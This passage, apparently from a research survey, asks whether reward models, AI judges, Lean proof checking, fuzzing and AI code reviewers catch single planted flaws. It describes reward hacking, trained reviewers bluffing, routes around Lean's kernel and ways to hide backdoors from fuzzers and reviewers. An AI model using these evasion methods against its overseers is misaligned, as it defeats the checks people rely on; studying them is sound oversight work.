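The unfounded assumption is the edit most like minimal sabotage. In the example, one added clause assumes that two numbers are both greater than 20, and the rest of the solution is unchanged. Qwen's average drop of 0.78 is a good result. Many of its scores fell by the full 1 point, but a substantial group hardly moved. Skywork's scores usually fell little. A small drop isn't always a mistake, because an assumption that no later step uses may do no harm.

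The paper is inconsistent about which flaws each model misses. According to its text, Skywork reliably penalises unrelated questions and Qwen mostly misses them, but Qwen's average drop is larger. According to a figure caption, Qwen misses the unfounded assumptions, but its average drop for those was large. The safer conclusion is that each model missed some kinds of broken logic.

In an earlier study, *Reward Models Identify Consistency, Not Causality*, Xu, Dong and colleagues (2025) found a similar pattern. Removing the question changed reward models' scores little, while changing its numbers changed them a lot. The researchers also used a 1.5B Skywork model to pick the best of 16 solutions. Averaged over four sets of problems, the picks were right 66.5% of the time when the model had the question and 66.1% when it didn't, compared with 64.4% for a single solution. The researchers conclude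 that reward models mainly measure whether a text is consistent. If so, the models have a fair chance of catching a number that clashes with the rest of the text, but less chance of catching a false step that fits its surroundings.

Style also affects some process reward models. *EST-PRM* (2026) tested five public models on 4,687 solutions with changes that didn't affect correctness, such as padding with extra steps. The models had different weaknesses, and the most accurate model on unaltered solutions wasn't necessarily the most robust.

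### High rewards for wrong answers

Tiwari and colleagues then trained a small language model, Qwen2.5-1.5B-Instruct, using a process reward model's score as the only reward. The problems came from the 2024 AIME, a difficult American school mathematics competition. They summarise the outcome as rewards above 0.9 with accuracy below 4%, but the results differed between the two runs.

With Skywork's 1.5B model, the reward climbed from about 0.1 to above 0.8, while accuracy peaked at 3–4%. To see what the trained model had learned, the researchers rephrased its solutions to problems from the 2025 competition, keeping the mathematics the same. Training had raised the average score from 0.246 to 0.641, and rephrasing cut it to 0.472. So 0.169 of the 0.395 gain, or 43%, came from wording. Rephrasing had hardly changed the larger Skywork model's scores on ordinary solutions. An evaluator whose scores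 hardly depend on style in ordinary text may therefore still reward style in text from a model trained against it.

With Qwen's 7B model, the reward reached 1.0 within about 100 training steps and accuracy fell to 0%. The trained model wrote only "Alright, let's solve this problem step by step." The reward for a solution was the lowest score among its steps, and this sentence made no claim that could be marked false.

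The low accuracy is partly due to the model being trained. Agrawal and colleagues trained a model of the same size with two other versions of the reward, and it got no AIME problems right with either. But the model's weakness can't explain why the rewards rose so high, since a sound evaluator would have kept scoring the bad solutions low. The outputs were also useless rather than subtly sabotaged, so the runs don't give a detection rate for small changes. They show that a high score is poor evidence of sound work when the model has had a chance to learn what the evaluator rewards.

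### Larger models, and judges that reason first

One objection is that most of these models were small, open and by now old. Size did help in one experiment. Tiwari and colleagues had an optimiser search for token strings that raise the scores of flawed solutions, and it was far more successful against the 1.5B Skywork model than against either 7B model. None of these studies tested the much stronger general models that now exist.

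Two recent experiments with single changes to code suggest that detection depends heavily on the model. *Honesty Is a Race* (2026) used programs that failed a hidden test because of one change, such as a swapped comparison or an off-by-one index. Qwen2.5-Coder-3B-Instruct, a small coding model, called 62% of the altered programs buggy, but also 29% of the correct ones.

The second experiment, in *Uncovering the Turing Test's Latent Signal* (2026), used DeepSeek V4 Flash, a much more capable open model from April 2026, with its reasoning switched off. The researchers changed one operator or constant in correct programs, for example `==` to `!=`, and kept the change if it made the program wrong. They scored each program only by how likely the model was to have written it. The correct version got the higher probability in 95% of comparisons. The change cut that probability about 17-fold on average,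 while adding a comment line altered it by a factor of about 1.8. This is strong evidence that a model's score can react to one decisive token.

In the same experiment, when the correct and incorrect programs were separate attempts at a task, the correct one got the higher probability only 78% of the time. Other differences between the programs could outweigh correctness, as in the toy example.

The other part of the reply is that judges which write out their reasoning may catch what a bare score misses. Agrawal and colleagues compare several evaluators on PRMBench, where the figures are for single steps:

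| Evaluator | Type | Detection rate | False-alarm rate | Balanced accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Math-PRM-7B | Score only | 31% | 5% | 63% |
| ThinkPRM-7B | Reasons first | 51% | 17% | 67% |
| GenPRM-7B | Reasons first | 74% | 48% | 63% |
| GPT-4o | General AI judge | 58% | 17% | 71% |

The two 7B models that reason before judging caught far more wrong steps but also rejected more correct ones. GenPRM's balanced accuracy is no better than the score-only model's, so its higher detection rate may come more from a stricter standard than from better judgment.

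Huang and colleagues report a larger advantage on long mathematical solutions. Most score-only reward models picked the correct one of two solutions about 70% of the time, while an April 2025 preview of Gemini 2.5 Flash did so 90% of the time. But when Gemini had to score each solution separately, as a monitor does, its result fell to 65%, because it often gave both the same score and a tie counted as a failure.

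Judges trained to look for differences have the same difficulty. *RightDiff* (Chen, Huang and colleagues, 2026) trained an 8B judge to list the differences between two outputs and label each one as material or immaterial before choosing. This directly addresses distraction by style, but it requires a second output for comparison. The judge scored 76.1% overall on RM-Bench, compared with 72.5% for an August 2024 version of GPT-4o and 82.6% for *Skywork-Reward-V2*, a score-only model built on the same Qwen3-8B base.

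## The case for checking by execution, counterexample and formal proof

Optimists and pessimists about learned evaluators disagree about how well a model can find flaws by reading. A third view is that nobody should have to rely on that. Whoever writes a program or proof, or the model that reviews it, should supply something a machine can test: a formal proof, an input that makes the program fail, or a record of what the program did when it ran. A tidy layout or confident tone doesn't affect such a test. The size of the flaw doesn't either, which makes the approach attractive against minimal sabotage.

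### How a proof assistant rejects one wrong step

A Lean theorem is a formal statement. Lean accepts a proof only if Lean's *kernel*, the small core program that does the final checking, confirms that the proof establishes exactly that statement. While a proof is unfinished, Lean keeps a list of goals, each with the facts available so far and the conclusion still to prove. As Wang, Wu and colleagues (2026) explain in *FaithSieve*, each command turns one list of goals into another, and the proof is complete only when no goals are left.

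In the earlier example with two swapped hypotheses, the goal looks like this:

```lean
h1 : a < b
h2 : b < c
⊢ a < c        -- the conclusion still to prove
```

The rule `lt_trans` takes a proof that x < y, then a proof that y < z, and returns a proof that x < z. With `h1` first, y is b in both inequalities, and the result closes the goal. If `h2` comes first, y is c, so the second inequality would have to start with c, but `h1` starts with a. Lean then reports an error and the goal stays open, no matter how many correct lines surround the bad one.

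A saboteur would therefore have to get around Lean's kernel. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* (Ammanamanchi, Bhat and Biderman, 2026) describes several ways to do this. One is to declare the theorem as an *axiom*, which Lean accepts without proof. Another is to use the command `native_decide`, which relies on Lean's whole compiler as well as the kernel. Compiler bugs have allowed proofs of contradictions. Before version 4.20.0, another bug let the command `apply?` report success for a theorem that had not passed the ordinary kernel check, and at least three proofs claimed for DeepSeek-Prover-V2 had this fault. Evaluators can close these gaps by using a patched version, listing the axioms behind each proof, and running `comparator`, a strict checker from the Lean community. Each fix protects every later proof, whereas a better prompt for an AI judge only changes its chance of catching sabotage.

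### Who checks the statement?

In the June blog post *Judge the Spec, Not the Proof*, Miranda (2026) argues that researchers are measuring the wrong thing when they test how well models grade written proofs. Miranda reasons that people want an AI judge because they can't audit a long argument line by line, but Lean can do that audit once the argument is formal, and its answer isn't another model's opinion. Miranda sees translating the theorem as the hard part, since an agent with Lean's tools can usually find the proof. The judge is then needed only to decide whether the formal theorem is the one people meant, which Lean can't do. Miranda considers a valid proof of the wrong statement worse than no proof.

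The argument holds only if the work can be formalized. Barkallah and colleagues point out that Lean's libraries are far from covering modern research mathematics, and that formalizing a research result can take experts months or years even with AI help. But where formalization is possible, Miranda's division of labor narrows the search for sabotage considerably, because a reviewer has to read only a few lines of statement and the definitions they use instead of 400 lines of proof.

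Those few lines can still go wrong in small ways. *The Faithfulness Gap* (2026) gives three Lean versions of the theorem that every continuous function on a compact set attains its maximum:

| Version | What it says | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Faithful | K is compact and not empty, and f is continuous on K. Some x in K has f(y) ≤ f(x) for every y in K. | True, and the intended theorem |
| Missing hypothesis | The same, but K may be empty. | False, since an empty set contains no x |
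| Swapped quantifiers | For every y in K, some x in K has f(y) ≤ f(x). | Trivially true: take x = y |

The second version would be useless to a saboteur because Lean will never accept a proof of it. The third is dangerous because it has a valid one-line proof, and someone who trusts the theorem's name may build on it. A saboteur could also give a theorem contradictory hypotheses, from which every conclusion follows. Ammanamanchi and colleagues found an accidental case of this in an early version of CombiBench, a set of combinatorics problems, where a badly written minimality condition was impossible to satisfy.

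Automatic checks covered about 10,000 problems from five Lean benchmarks and their variants. In 398 cases they produced a mechanical certificate that something was wrong, such as a counterexample or a proof that the hypotheses contradict each other. Some of these cases are copies of the same problem, so the count isn't an error rate. These checks can expose a false or empty statement, but they can't detect when a true, meaningful statement is weaker than the one intended.

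Models can get the formal statement wrong without trying to. In *Beyond Compilation*, Zhang, Gallardo Candela and colleagues (2026) asked models to translate 227 university-level statements into Lean. An agent built on GPT-5.2 produced statements that compiled 87.2% of the time, but two AI judges accepted only 57.7% of the 227 as faithful. Human reviewers confirmed that 54 of the 67 compiled statements the judges rejected were wrong, which is nearly a quarter of all the translations.

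Newer models do far better. For GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5.5, a review attributed only 4 of 54 rejections to translation errors, or about 1% of all their translations. Claude Opus 5.5 was one of the two reviewing models, and the review didn't cover accepted statements. OpenAI and Anthropic have since released newer models.

A low rate of accidental errors in formal statements helps less against someone who chooses the error, so it matters whether the judges of the statement would notice it. In one sample, human reviewers and the two judges, GPT-5.2 and Gemini-2.5-Pro, scored the output of Aristotle, a formal reasoning system. Of the 53 statements that compiled, 6 were unfaithful, and the judges caught 4 of them. They also rejected 3 of the 47 faithful statements. The sample is small, but it gives no reason to think that judging statements is easy for these models.

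### The faulty statement that model checks missed

*M2F* (Wang, Ma and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that translates mathematical texts into Lean and proves the results. The system keeps an edit only if Lean confirms that it reduces the number of errors or unproved gaps. In about three weeks, it turned 479 pages, mostly from two textbooks, into 153,853 lines of Lean.

The researchers also ran M2F's proving stage on FATE-H, a set of 100 algebra problems already stated in Lean, and it proved 96. One of the remaining four had an inconsistent statement that nobody could prove. The researchers found the inconsistency from the record of M2F's failed attempts, and an expert confirmed it. Several models, including GPT-5.2 Pro, had already checked the statement's meaning, and none had flagged the problem.

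This supports the third view, since a mechanical check exposed a fault that judges had missed. But the check caught it only because the statement was unprovable. If the same fault had made the theorem too weak, M2F would have proved it, and the benchmark would have recorded a success.

Wang, Ma and colleagues used a human expert to check that the textbook theorems and lemmas M2F had to prove were stated faithfully. The expert compared every one with the source text, looking at quantifiers, side conditions and added assumptions, and the audit led to no corrections. The researchers argue that a model's approval isn't proof of faithfulness, because models wrote the statements and models that review them may share the same blind spots.

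An audit like this is useless if the prover can change the statement afterwards. *FATE* (2025), which introduced the algebra problems, guards against this with a program that confirms the original definitions and theorem appear word for word in the submission before Lean checks it. Lean then confirms that the proof contains no errors and no `sorry`, the placeholder for a missing proof. These checks leave very little room for sabotage by someone who controls only the proof. Someone who writes the definitions or the theorem can still do harm, so a different party should write or audit those.

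### Running new code beside the old

Most software has no formal specification, but anyone can run it and watch what it does. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) presents Lily, a tool that looks for newly added backdoors this way. Lily uses *fuzzing* rather than a learned evaluator. Fuzzing means running a program on many automatically altered inputs and keeping those that reach new parts of the code.

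Lily records the *system calls* that each input triggers, that is, the program's requests to the operating system, such as opening a file or starting another program. The set of call types for one input is its profile. When a change comes in, Lily works as follows:

1. It runs the new version on inputs saved from earlier fuzzing and records the profiles as normal behavior.
2. It fuzzes the new version for ten minutes and picks out any input whose profile isn't among the normal ones.
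3. It runs that input on the old version. If the old version produces the same profile, the change didn't cause it. If not, Lily raises an alarm.
4. It traces the unusual calls back to the changed lines responsible.

One test case is the real backdoor that attackers put into vsFTPd, a file server, in 2011. A username containing ":)" opened a command shell with full control of the machine. When the fuzzer generates such a name, the program makes a combination of network and process calls that no earlier input produced and that the previous release doesn't make for the same name. Lily's report then narrows 1,407 changed lines to seven.

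The researchers tested Lily on 13 open-source programs, with three real backdoors and ten synthetic ones, and repeated every test 20 times because fuzzing is random.

| | Detection rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|
| Single commits | 90% (233 of 260 runs) | 0.2% (17 of 8,640 runs) |
| Whole releases | 83% (828 of 1,000 runs) | 4.3% (43 of 1,000 runs) |

These figures are shares of runs, and Lily caught every backdoor in at least one run, so running it again helps. The lowest detection rates, down to 39% of runs, came from old releases for which the developers' *harness*, the code that feeds inputs to the program, was still immature. The false alarms for releases were much less random. Two releases of the sound library libsndfile set off the alarm every time and accounted for 40 of the 43.

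The false-alarm rate is low because Lily flags only behavior that is both new and unusual. Flagging all new behavior would have raised false alarms in 10% of the commit runs, and flagging all unusual behavior in 14%.

A 90% detection rate with 0.2% false alarms is far better than the AI judges of proofs achieved, but the tasks differ. Most of these backdoors do something drastic, such as running an attacker's commands or encrypting the home directory. The `or` that replaced an `and` in the earlier access check is harder to catch. Lily did catch hard-coded credentials in the Unix tool Sudo in all its runs, so some login bypasses change the profile. But if the saved inputs already include a normal administrator's visit, an intruder's visit could produce the same system calls, and Lily would treat it as safe. A search that stops after five candidates would probably not change the profile.

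Fuzzing also has to reach the bad code. In 337 commits that Kokkonis and colleagues examined, it reached an average of about 32% of the lines it could in principle have covered. An attacker can hide a backdoor behind a cryptographic check that random inputs will almost never pass. The attackers of XZ Utils, a compression library, did this in 2024 and also switched off the project's fuzzing.

An attacker can also add backdoor-triggering inputs to the saved set, so that Lily treats the resulting behavior as normal. With 100 such inputs, the detection rate for commits fell to 54%. A hardened mode restored it to 90% but raised the false alarm rate from 0.2% to about 2.5%.

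### Paying for counterexamples

Lily can detect only bugs that change system calls. A more general rule requires anyone who reports a bug to give an input on which the program returns the wrong result. *Honesty Is a Race*, the November 2026 study of one-place changes to short Python functions, examines the effects of training a model under this rule.

In one example, the function should return the n-th term of an arithmetic progression:

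```python
tn = a + (n - 1) * d   # sound
tn = a + (n - 2) * d   # altered
```

The model sees one version along with the specification. It can answer "correct", or answer "buggy" and name an input, such as a = 1, n = 5, d = 2. A checker runs both versions on that input, gets 9 from the sound one and 7 from the altered one, and accepts the counterexample. No comparable check can confirm "correct", since a program can pass some tests and still fail on other inputs. The study therefore rewards the answer "correct" without checking it, as if the available tests missed the bug in every altered program.

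Let b be the payment for "correct", r the payment for a valid counterexample, and p the chance that the model's counterexample is valid. An invalid counterexample earns nothing. On a buggy program:

payment for "correct" = b

expected payment for "buggy" with a counterexample = p · r

Reporting the bug therefore has the higher expected reward only if p · r > b. For a version of Qwen2.5-Coder-3B that the researchers had fine-tuned for the task, p was 0.735. With b = 0.3, r had to exceed 0.3 / 0.735, or about 0.41. If r is lower, the model gets more reward on average by *bluffing*, which here means calling a buggy program correct.

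Training follows the same comparison. The method samples a group of answers to one problem and reinforces those that earn more than the group's average. If k of n answers say "correct" and the rest report a bug, the expected average is (k · b + (n − k) · p · r) / n. The expected advantage of saying "correct" is then:

b − average = ((n − k) / n) · (b − p · r)

The sign depends only on b − p · r. When this difference is positive, every group containing both kinds of answer pushes the model towards bluffing, however few of its answers are bluffs at the start.

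The table shows the final results for the two code models, the Qwen model and Microsoft's Phi-3.5-mini. Any "buggy" verdict on an altered program counts as a detection, even if the counterexample fails.

| Value of p · r / b | Qwen: detection rate | Qwen: false-alarm rate | Phi: detection rate | Phi: false-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before this training | 66% | 20% | 65% | 26% |
| 0.95 | 0% | 0% | 3% | 0% |
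| 1.25 | 39% | 3% | 49% | 6% |
| 2 | 74% | 21% | 66% | 22% |
| 3 | 93% | 55% | 87% | 48% |

Just below break-even, both models learned to approve nearly everything. At a value of 1.25, both first fell almost to zero and were still recovering when training ended. The simple comparison leaves out the sound programs, for which "correct" is the right answer. Training on them makes the model more likely to say "correct" on buggy programs too, until it has learned how to treat the sound ones. At 3, the effect carries over in the opposite direction, and the models called about half of the sound programs buggy. The best value tested was 2.

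On a companion task in formal logic, the researchers tested whether a model that had learned to bluff still distinguished true claims from false ones internally. Before training, they had fitted a simple classifier to the model's activations to separate the two. After the collapse, the classifier still ranked a true claim above a false one 92–99% of the time, so the model had kept the distinction but stopped reporting it. Too large a reward for unchecked approval can therefore make a reviewer stop reporting bugs it is able to detect.

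These are small models, with one training run for each setting on code, so the exact percentages matter less than the direction.

Requiring a counterexample also removes false alarms, because no input can make a sound program differ from itself. Someone who acted only on confirmed counterexamples could ignore the 55% in the table. But the detection rate would also fall. At a ratio of 2, about 80% of the Qwen model's counterexamples were valid, so roughly 59% of the bugs would be confirmed. This checker also needs a sound version of the program to compare against, as the kernel developers had in 2003. For new code, someone has to work out the right output from the specification, and if the specification doesn't cover that input, nobody can confirm the counterexample.

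### Bringing the checks to written proofs

Two recent methods try to give ordinary written proofs some of the advantages of formal ones. In *pseudo-formalization*, proposed by Barkallah and colleagues, a model rewrites the proof as separate modules, still in natural language. Each module states its premises, its conclusion and the argument between them. A model then checks one module at a time, seeing only that module and the exact statements it relies on. In the earlier example about d and −d, this puts the lemma's wording next to the step that overstates it. A final call to the model decides which reported faults are serious.

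Barkallah and colleagues compared this with asking the same model to judge the original text:

- On the olympiad-level solutions of Hard2Verify, GPT-5.4 mini found around 90% of the wrong steps either way when it read each solution eight times. Pseudo-formalization wrongly flagged 28% fewer steps per proof.
- On 100 research papers whose authors had later disclosed an error, it found more of the errors than direct judging did, but eight readings still missed roughly 40% of them.
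- On 16 AI-written proofs of research problems, with 24 errors identified by expert referees, GPT-5.5 at high reasoning effort found 66% of the errors in one reading, against 54% for direct judging. About three quarters of its complaints were right under either method.

The gain is real but limited, and the final check still relies on a model's judgment. The rewriting can also change the proof. Barkallah and colleagues compare the rewritten proof with the original and repair discrepancies, but a model has to make that comparison too.

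FaithSieve, a system by Wang, Wu and colleagues, uses Lean to check some steps of a proof. A model splits the proof into small transitions, each from one set of known facts and goals to the next, and picks out suspicious ones. It turns these into explicit claims and translates them into Lean, where a prover tries to prove or refute them. A calculator program checks simple arithmetic instead.

Splitting a proof into steps matters because a strong prover can otherwise hide an error. Suppose a proof derives b from a, and then c from b, and the first step is false. If c happens to follow from a by another route, the prover can establish that a implies c without testing the false step. Naik and colleagues saw something similar when AI judges silently repaired proofs.

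Wang, Wu and colleagues measured how often the system gave exactly the right answer, which meant naming the first wrong step or recognizing that the proof was valid:

| Proofs | GPT-5.4 alone | GPT-5.4 with FaithSieve | Qwen3.5-9B alone | Qwen3.5-9B with FaithSieve |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 350 olympiad-style | 72.3% | 81.4% | 53.7% | 74.0% |
| 200 university-level | 75.0% | 84.5% | 61.0% | 69.5% |

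For the small Qwen model, most of the gain on olympiad-style proofs came from splitting the proof up, which brought it to 71.1% without any formal checking. GPT-5.4 reached only 73.4% without formal checking, so more of its gain came from the formal evidence. That evidence helped only when the Lean statements were faithful. When the researchers loosened the filter for meaning, GPT-5.4's result dropped to 70.9%, slightly worse than without FaithSieve.

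That filter is itself a learned evaluator, and it is weak. Two experts reviewed 135 of the Lean statements it had judged and found 20 unfaithful. The filter had caught only 7 of these (35%) and had wrongly rejected about 9% of the faithful ones. Some of the 13 it missed were trivially true, and others had added assumptions or weaker conclusions, which are changes a saboteur would want. Splitting the proof also carries a risk, since 7 of 50 audited proofs no longer had their first error intact afterwards. All the errors in FaithSieve's tests were unintentional mistakes by GPT-4o, so no one has measured how well it catches planted ones.

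### Properties that nobody specified

A machine check covers only the property that somebody wrote down. For the access check, a developer might prove the first of these two theorems and forget the second:

```lean
theorem admits   : admin ∧ valid → allowed   -- true of both versions
theorem excludes : allowed → admin ∧ valid   -- false if `and` became `or`
```

The first theorem is that an administrator with a valid session gets in. The sabotaged code satisfies it, so Lean will accept the proof, and a reviewer may see "formally verified" next to code that lets any logged-in user through. Proving only this theorem is an easy mistake, because people tend to specify what a program should do and forget to specify what it must never do.

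Quietly degraded work is harder to rule out with a specification. A specification that requires the best of all the candidates would expose the search that stops after five candidates, but often nobody can define the ideal result that precisely, and nobody can prove how good a research summary or a software design could have been.

The time and effort required limit the approach even where people know what to specify. Each run of Lily takes ten minutes on four processor cores, which is practical for many projects, but formal proof of software takes much more work. *AutoSpec* (Li and Wang, 2026) provides tools that translate existing Rust programs into Lean, so that agents can prove properties of them, and a benchmark of 159 cases, all algorithms. Li and Wang found that agents struggled to structure the proofs and to learn techniques specific to verification.

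Whole projects are harder to verify than single functions. *Vero* (2026) tests agents on writing both the code and the proofs for 43 multi-module projects. The best agent met over 80% of the individual specifications, but it couldn't keep a whole project consistent and able to build. It failed to find the shared invariants, the conditions that several modules must all preserve. Until agents can do this, developers will probably have to reserve formal proof for small, critical parts of their software and check the rest in other ways.

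## Do judges notice one harmful change in code?

Most code will never be formally proved correct, so its main protection is that somebody reads each change before it is added to the project. On sites such as GitHub, a developer proposes a change as a *pull request*, which consists of the added and deleted lines (the *diff*), a title and a description. If the reviewers raise no serious objection, a maintainer merges the change. Several companies now offer AI judges that review pull requests, and anyone who wants to plant one harmful line has to get it past them.

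*From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) introduces MalPR-Bench, a benchmark that measures how well such reviewers do. It contains 89 malicious pull requests and 50 sound ones from 44 code repositories. It assumes that a hostile author controls the whole pull request, including its comments and tests, so the reviewer can't trust any of it.

### How the malicious cases came about

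No real saboteur wrote these pull requests. The researchers reconstructed most of them from mistakes that real projects had made and later fixed:

| Group | Where the flaw comes from | Malicious | Sound |
|---|---|---|---|
| Development | Old security fixes that left a related path open | 14 | 0 |
| Project histories | The same, from other projects | 19 | 6 |
| Withheld protection | A real fix with one of its new checks left out | 7 | 7 |
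| Removed protection | A real fix reversed in one place, so that the diff deletes a check | 37 | 37 |
| Production | Previously unknown flaws in widely used projects | 12 | 0 |

Chen and colleagues used the 14 development cases only to build their own reviewer, PRGuard, so the test results cover the other 75.

The removed protections come closest to minimal sabotage, because the researchers deliberately removed only one check. The matching sound pull request is the project's complete fix. A reviewer can often tell the two apart by whether the diff deletes a check or adds one, which makes these pairs easier in that respect than true minimal pairs.

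### Blocking a change for the wrong reason

The benchmark scores the verdict and the diagnosis separately. A reviewer gets the verdict right if it blocks a malicious pull request. The diagnosis must state which behaviour is affected, which protection is missing or broken, and what harm follows. A further score requires the review to point to the code that proves the flaw. Chen and colleagues fixed the acceptable answers for each case before grading. Two language models proposed the diagnosis scores, and two people settled the disagreements and checked some of the rest.

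One of the production cases shows what a verdict alone can hide. An automation platform had added a way to resume a paused run of an AI agent. The user sends the run's identifier, and the server looks up the saved state. In simplified form (this is a sketch, not the project's code):

```ts
requireAccess(user, url.projectId)                  // may this user enter this project?
run = checkpoints.find(body.runId)                  // flawed: finds runs from any project
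run = checkpoints.find(body.runId, url.projectId)   // sound: finds only this project's runs
```

The software checks that the user has access to the project named in the web address, but it then looks up the run by its identifier alone, without checking that the run belongs to that project. A user of one project who has a valid run identifier from another can therefore open the other project's saved conversation and approve an action that its agent was waiting to take. The researchers confirmed this on a running copy of the software.

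The lookup was in an existing file that the pull request didn't change, so a reviewer had to follow the new code into that file to see the problem. CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial AI reviewer, blocked the pull request, but the reason it gave was an unrelated problem with how a secret appeared in the user's browser. Fixing that problem would have left the security hole in place.

If a reviewer blocks a harmful change for the wrong reason, the block might still help when the developer is honest, because it gives people a reason to look again. It helps much less against a saboteur, who can fix the reported problem, resubmit, and hope the reviewer has no other objection.

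### CodeRabbit and PRGuard on the same cases

PRGuard tries to avoid wrong diagnoses by splitting the review into steps. Ordinary programs first collect related code, such as functions that call the changed code and similar functions elsewhere. A language model then describes what changed without proposing flaws. Another call to the model proposes specific flaws, and a separate call tests each one against the code. PRGuard then follows a fixed rule to block the change if a proposed flaw passes the test, comment if the evidence is incomplete, and otherwise approve. The researchers ran PRGuard with two models, GPT-5.5 and DeepSeek v4-pro.

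CodeRabbit doesn't disclose its model. Chen and colleagues counted it as blocking a pull request if it raised a security problem that it rated critical or major. Because of its cost and usage limits, they ran it on only 31 malicious cases, the 19 from project histories and the 12 from production. The table compares it with the DeepSeek version of PRGuard:

| Cases | CodeRabbit blocked | CodeRabbit named the flaw | PRGuard blocked | PRGuard named the flaw |
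|---|---|---|---|---|
| All 31 | 24 | 16 | 22 | 22 |
| A needed check is missing (14) | 9 | 3 | 9 | 9 |
| The flaw is in code that is present (17) | 15 | 13 | 13 | 13 |
| From project histories (19) | 14 | 12 | 12 | 12 |
| From production (12) | 10 | 4 | 10 | 10 |

CodeRabbit had a detection rate of 77%, but it named the real flaw in only 52% of cases. The gap comes mostly from pull requests that are missing a necessary check. No line in them is wrong, so the reviewer has to infer that a check should be there.

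The study's totals are weak evidence that PRGuard is a better reviewer than CodeRabbit. PRGuard, running on GPT-5.5, originally found the 12 production flaws, so they are flaws of a kind its method can find. The DeepSeek version ran independently but uses the same method. On the 19 cases that PRGuard didn't select, the two reviewers named the same number of flaws. CodeRabbit did slightly better on the strictest measure, with 12 blocks that named the flaw and proved it, against PRGuard's 9. The study is still good evidence that a reviewer can block a change for the wrong reason.

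Chen and colleagues also ran CodeQL, a tool that searches code for known dangerous patterns without using a language model. Its standard security rules applied to 21 of the 31 cases. CodeQL identified none of the flaws, and its one serious alert was about something else.

### Removed checks are easier to spot than missing ones

Both versions of PRGuard named the flaw in all 37 cases where the diff visibly removed a protection, which was the best result in the study. But the DeepSeek version blocked only 33 of these changes, and the GPT-5.5 version only 26. A project that used the GPT-5.5 version and merged whatever it didn't block would have accepted 11 sabotaged changes whose flaws the reviewer had named.

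Both versions wrongly blocked 3 of the 37 matching sound pull requests. Over all 50 sound ones, the false-alarm rate was 10% with GPT-5.5 and 8% with DeepSeek. CodeRabbit blocked none of the six it reviewed. All these sound pull requests are complete security fixes, so the rates may differ for everyday changes. Nobody ran CodeRabbit on the removed protections, so its detection rate for them is unknown.

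When the researchers reran PRGuard on the cases with withheld or removed protections, its verdict changed in up to 25% of them, but it switched between naming and missing the flaw in only about 7%. Anyone relying on such a reviewer to catch harmful changes should probably read its comments as well as its verdict.

PRGuard did much worse on missing checks. In the seven pull requests where the researchers had left one check out of a real fix, each version of PRGuard blocked four and named the flaw in three. To test how much the surrounding code mattered, Chen and colleagues gave PRGuard only the diff for these seven cases and five similar ones from project histories. The GPT-5.5 version then blocked one of the 12, for the wrong reason, and the DeepSeek version blocked none. With the full method, they blocked six and five, respectively.

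To show that a check is missing, a reviewer usually needs to compare the code with something, such as another function that performs the same operation and includes the check. CodeRabbit named none of the seven flaws whose evidence was outside the files the pull request changed, compared with 16 of the other 24. Four of those seven came from PRGuard's own discoveries, but CodeRabbit also missed the other three.

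A reviewer may miss the flaw even when it can search anywhere. The researchers ran OpenAI's Codex agent twice on each of seven cases, with free access to the whole repository. It named the flaw in three of the four cases where the evidence was in a file the pull request changed. In the other three cases, the evidence was in comparable code elsewhere, with no direct link from the change. Codex blocked those pull requests in four of six runs but never named the flaw. Seven hand-picked cases are weak evidence, though the failures look like CodeRabbit's.

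### What newer models catch

Newer models do better at naming flaws. In *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?*, Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026) collected 265 real changes to nine large projects, including Firefox and OpenSSL. Nearly all had introduced a security flaw, and a few were repairs that had failed to remove one. Each AI reviewer got the diff, the change's message and the full code, but no hint about the flaw. It got credit only if it explained the flaw's cause, and Claude Opus 5.5 judged the explanations.

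| Reviewer | Named the flaw | Reported only other things | Reported nothing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.6 | 207 (78%) | 53 | 5 |
| GPT-6 sol | 202 (76%) | 49 | 14 |
| GLM 5.3 | 198 (75%) | 66 | 1 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 196 (74%) | 63 | 6 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 157 (59%) | 100 | 8 |
| GPT-5.6 sol | 148 (56%) | 76 | 41 |
| GPT-6 luna | 147 (55%) | 76 | 42 |
| MiniMax M3 | 86 (32%) | 126 | 53 |

The top four are too close to rank. Models within one family improved quickly. GPT-6 sol found 58 flaws that GPT-5.6 sol had missed, and missed only four that the older model had found. The test included no Gemini model, and OpenAI and Anthropic have since released newer models.

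Grok 4.6 reported something in 98% of the reviews, but that figure counts any complaint, whether or not it identified the flaw. Yang and colleagues also had the models review repaired versions of the same changes. In about three quarters of those reviews, the models still reported a problem in a file that had held the flaw. Some of the reports may describe other, real problems, so this isn't a false-alarm rate. Even so, a complaint about the right file is weak evidence that the flaw is there.

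Wrong explanations also accounted for 68% of the misses, in which the reviewer reported a problem in the right file but described a different mechanism. For example, a nine-line change to curl left a pointer to memory that the program had already freed. All eight reviewers reported a problem in that file, but four thought the program failed to free the memory, which is roughly the opposite mistake, and the GPT models called the line a logic bug.

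Using several reviewers catches more flaws, but the reviewers tend to miss the same ones. The best three together found about nine in ten of the flaws, but all eight together still missed 23, far more than they would have if their mistakes were independent. Adding another model to a panel therefore protects less than multiplying the miss rates would suggest.

These flaws were accidental, and all had made it into the project, so the set excludes any that the original reviewers caught. It also leans towards memory errors. On average, the models found nearly three in four of the memory errors but only about half of the logic errors, which include mistakes like a wrong `or` in an access check.

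### Large changes and distant evidence

The size of a pull request also affects whether a reviewer catches a bug. *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?* (Yang, He and colleagues, 2026) introduces CRBugBench, a benchmark of 1,000 changes to open-source projects and 800 to two company repositories, each containing a bug that people had found. A reviewer catches the bug if its top five comments include it. On the open-source changes, Claude Opus 4.6 caught 47.7% of the bugs and Claude Opus 5, about five months newer, caught 71.9%. Opus 5 caught 64.2% of the half that people had noticed only after merging. The best models did up to 25.5% worse on the company code, where fewer bugs were visible in the diff.

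The researchers then estimated how each property of a change affects detection, holding the others constant. Increasing the size by one standard deviation (on a logarithmic scale) multiplied the odds of catching the bug by about 0.59, which would lower a 70% chance of detection to about 58%. The odds were 2.6 times as high when the bug was visible in the diff as when finding it required other code, knowledge of the project or a test run. A saboteur can choose the size of the change and the location of the evidence to avoid detection, while honest developers make these choices for other reasons.

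*PRWeaver* (2026) is a benchmark for testing AI reviewers on long-horizon malicious pull requests under varied conditions. It contains 208 attacks that work when run, in 832 matched versions.

### Reviewers that see the defect and approve anyway

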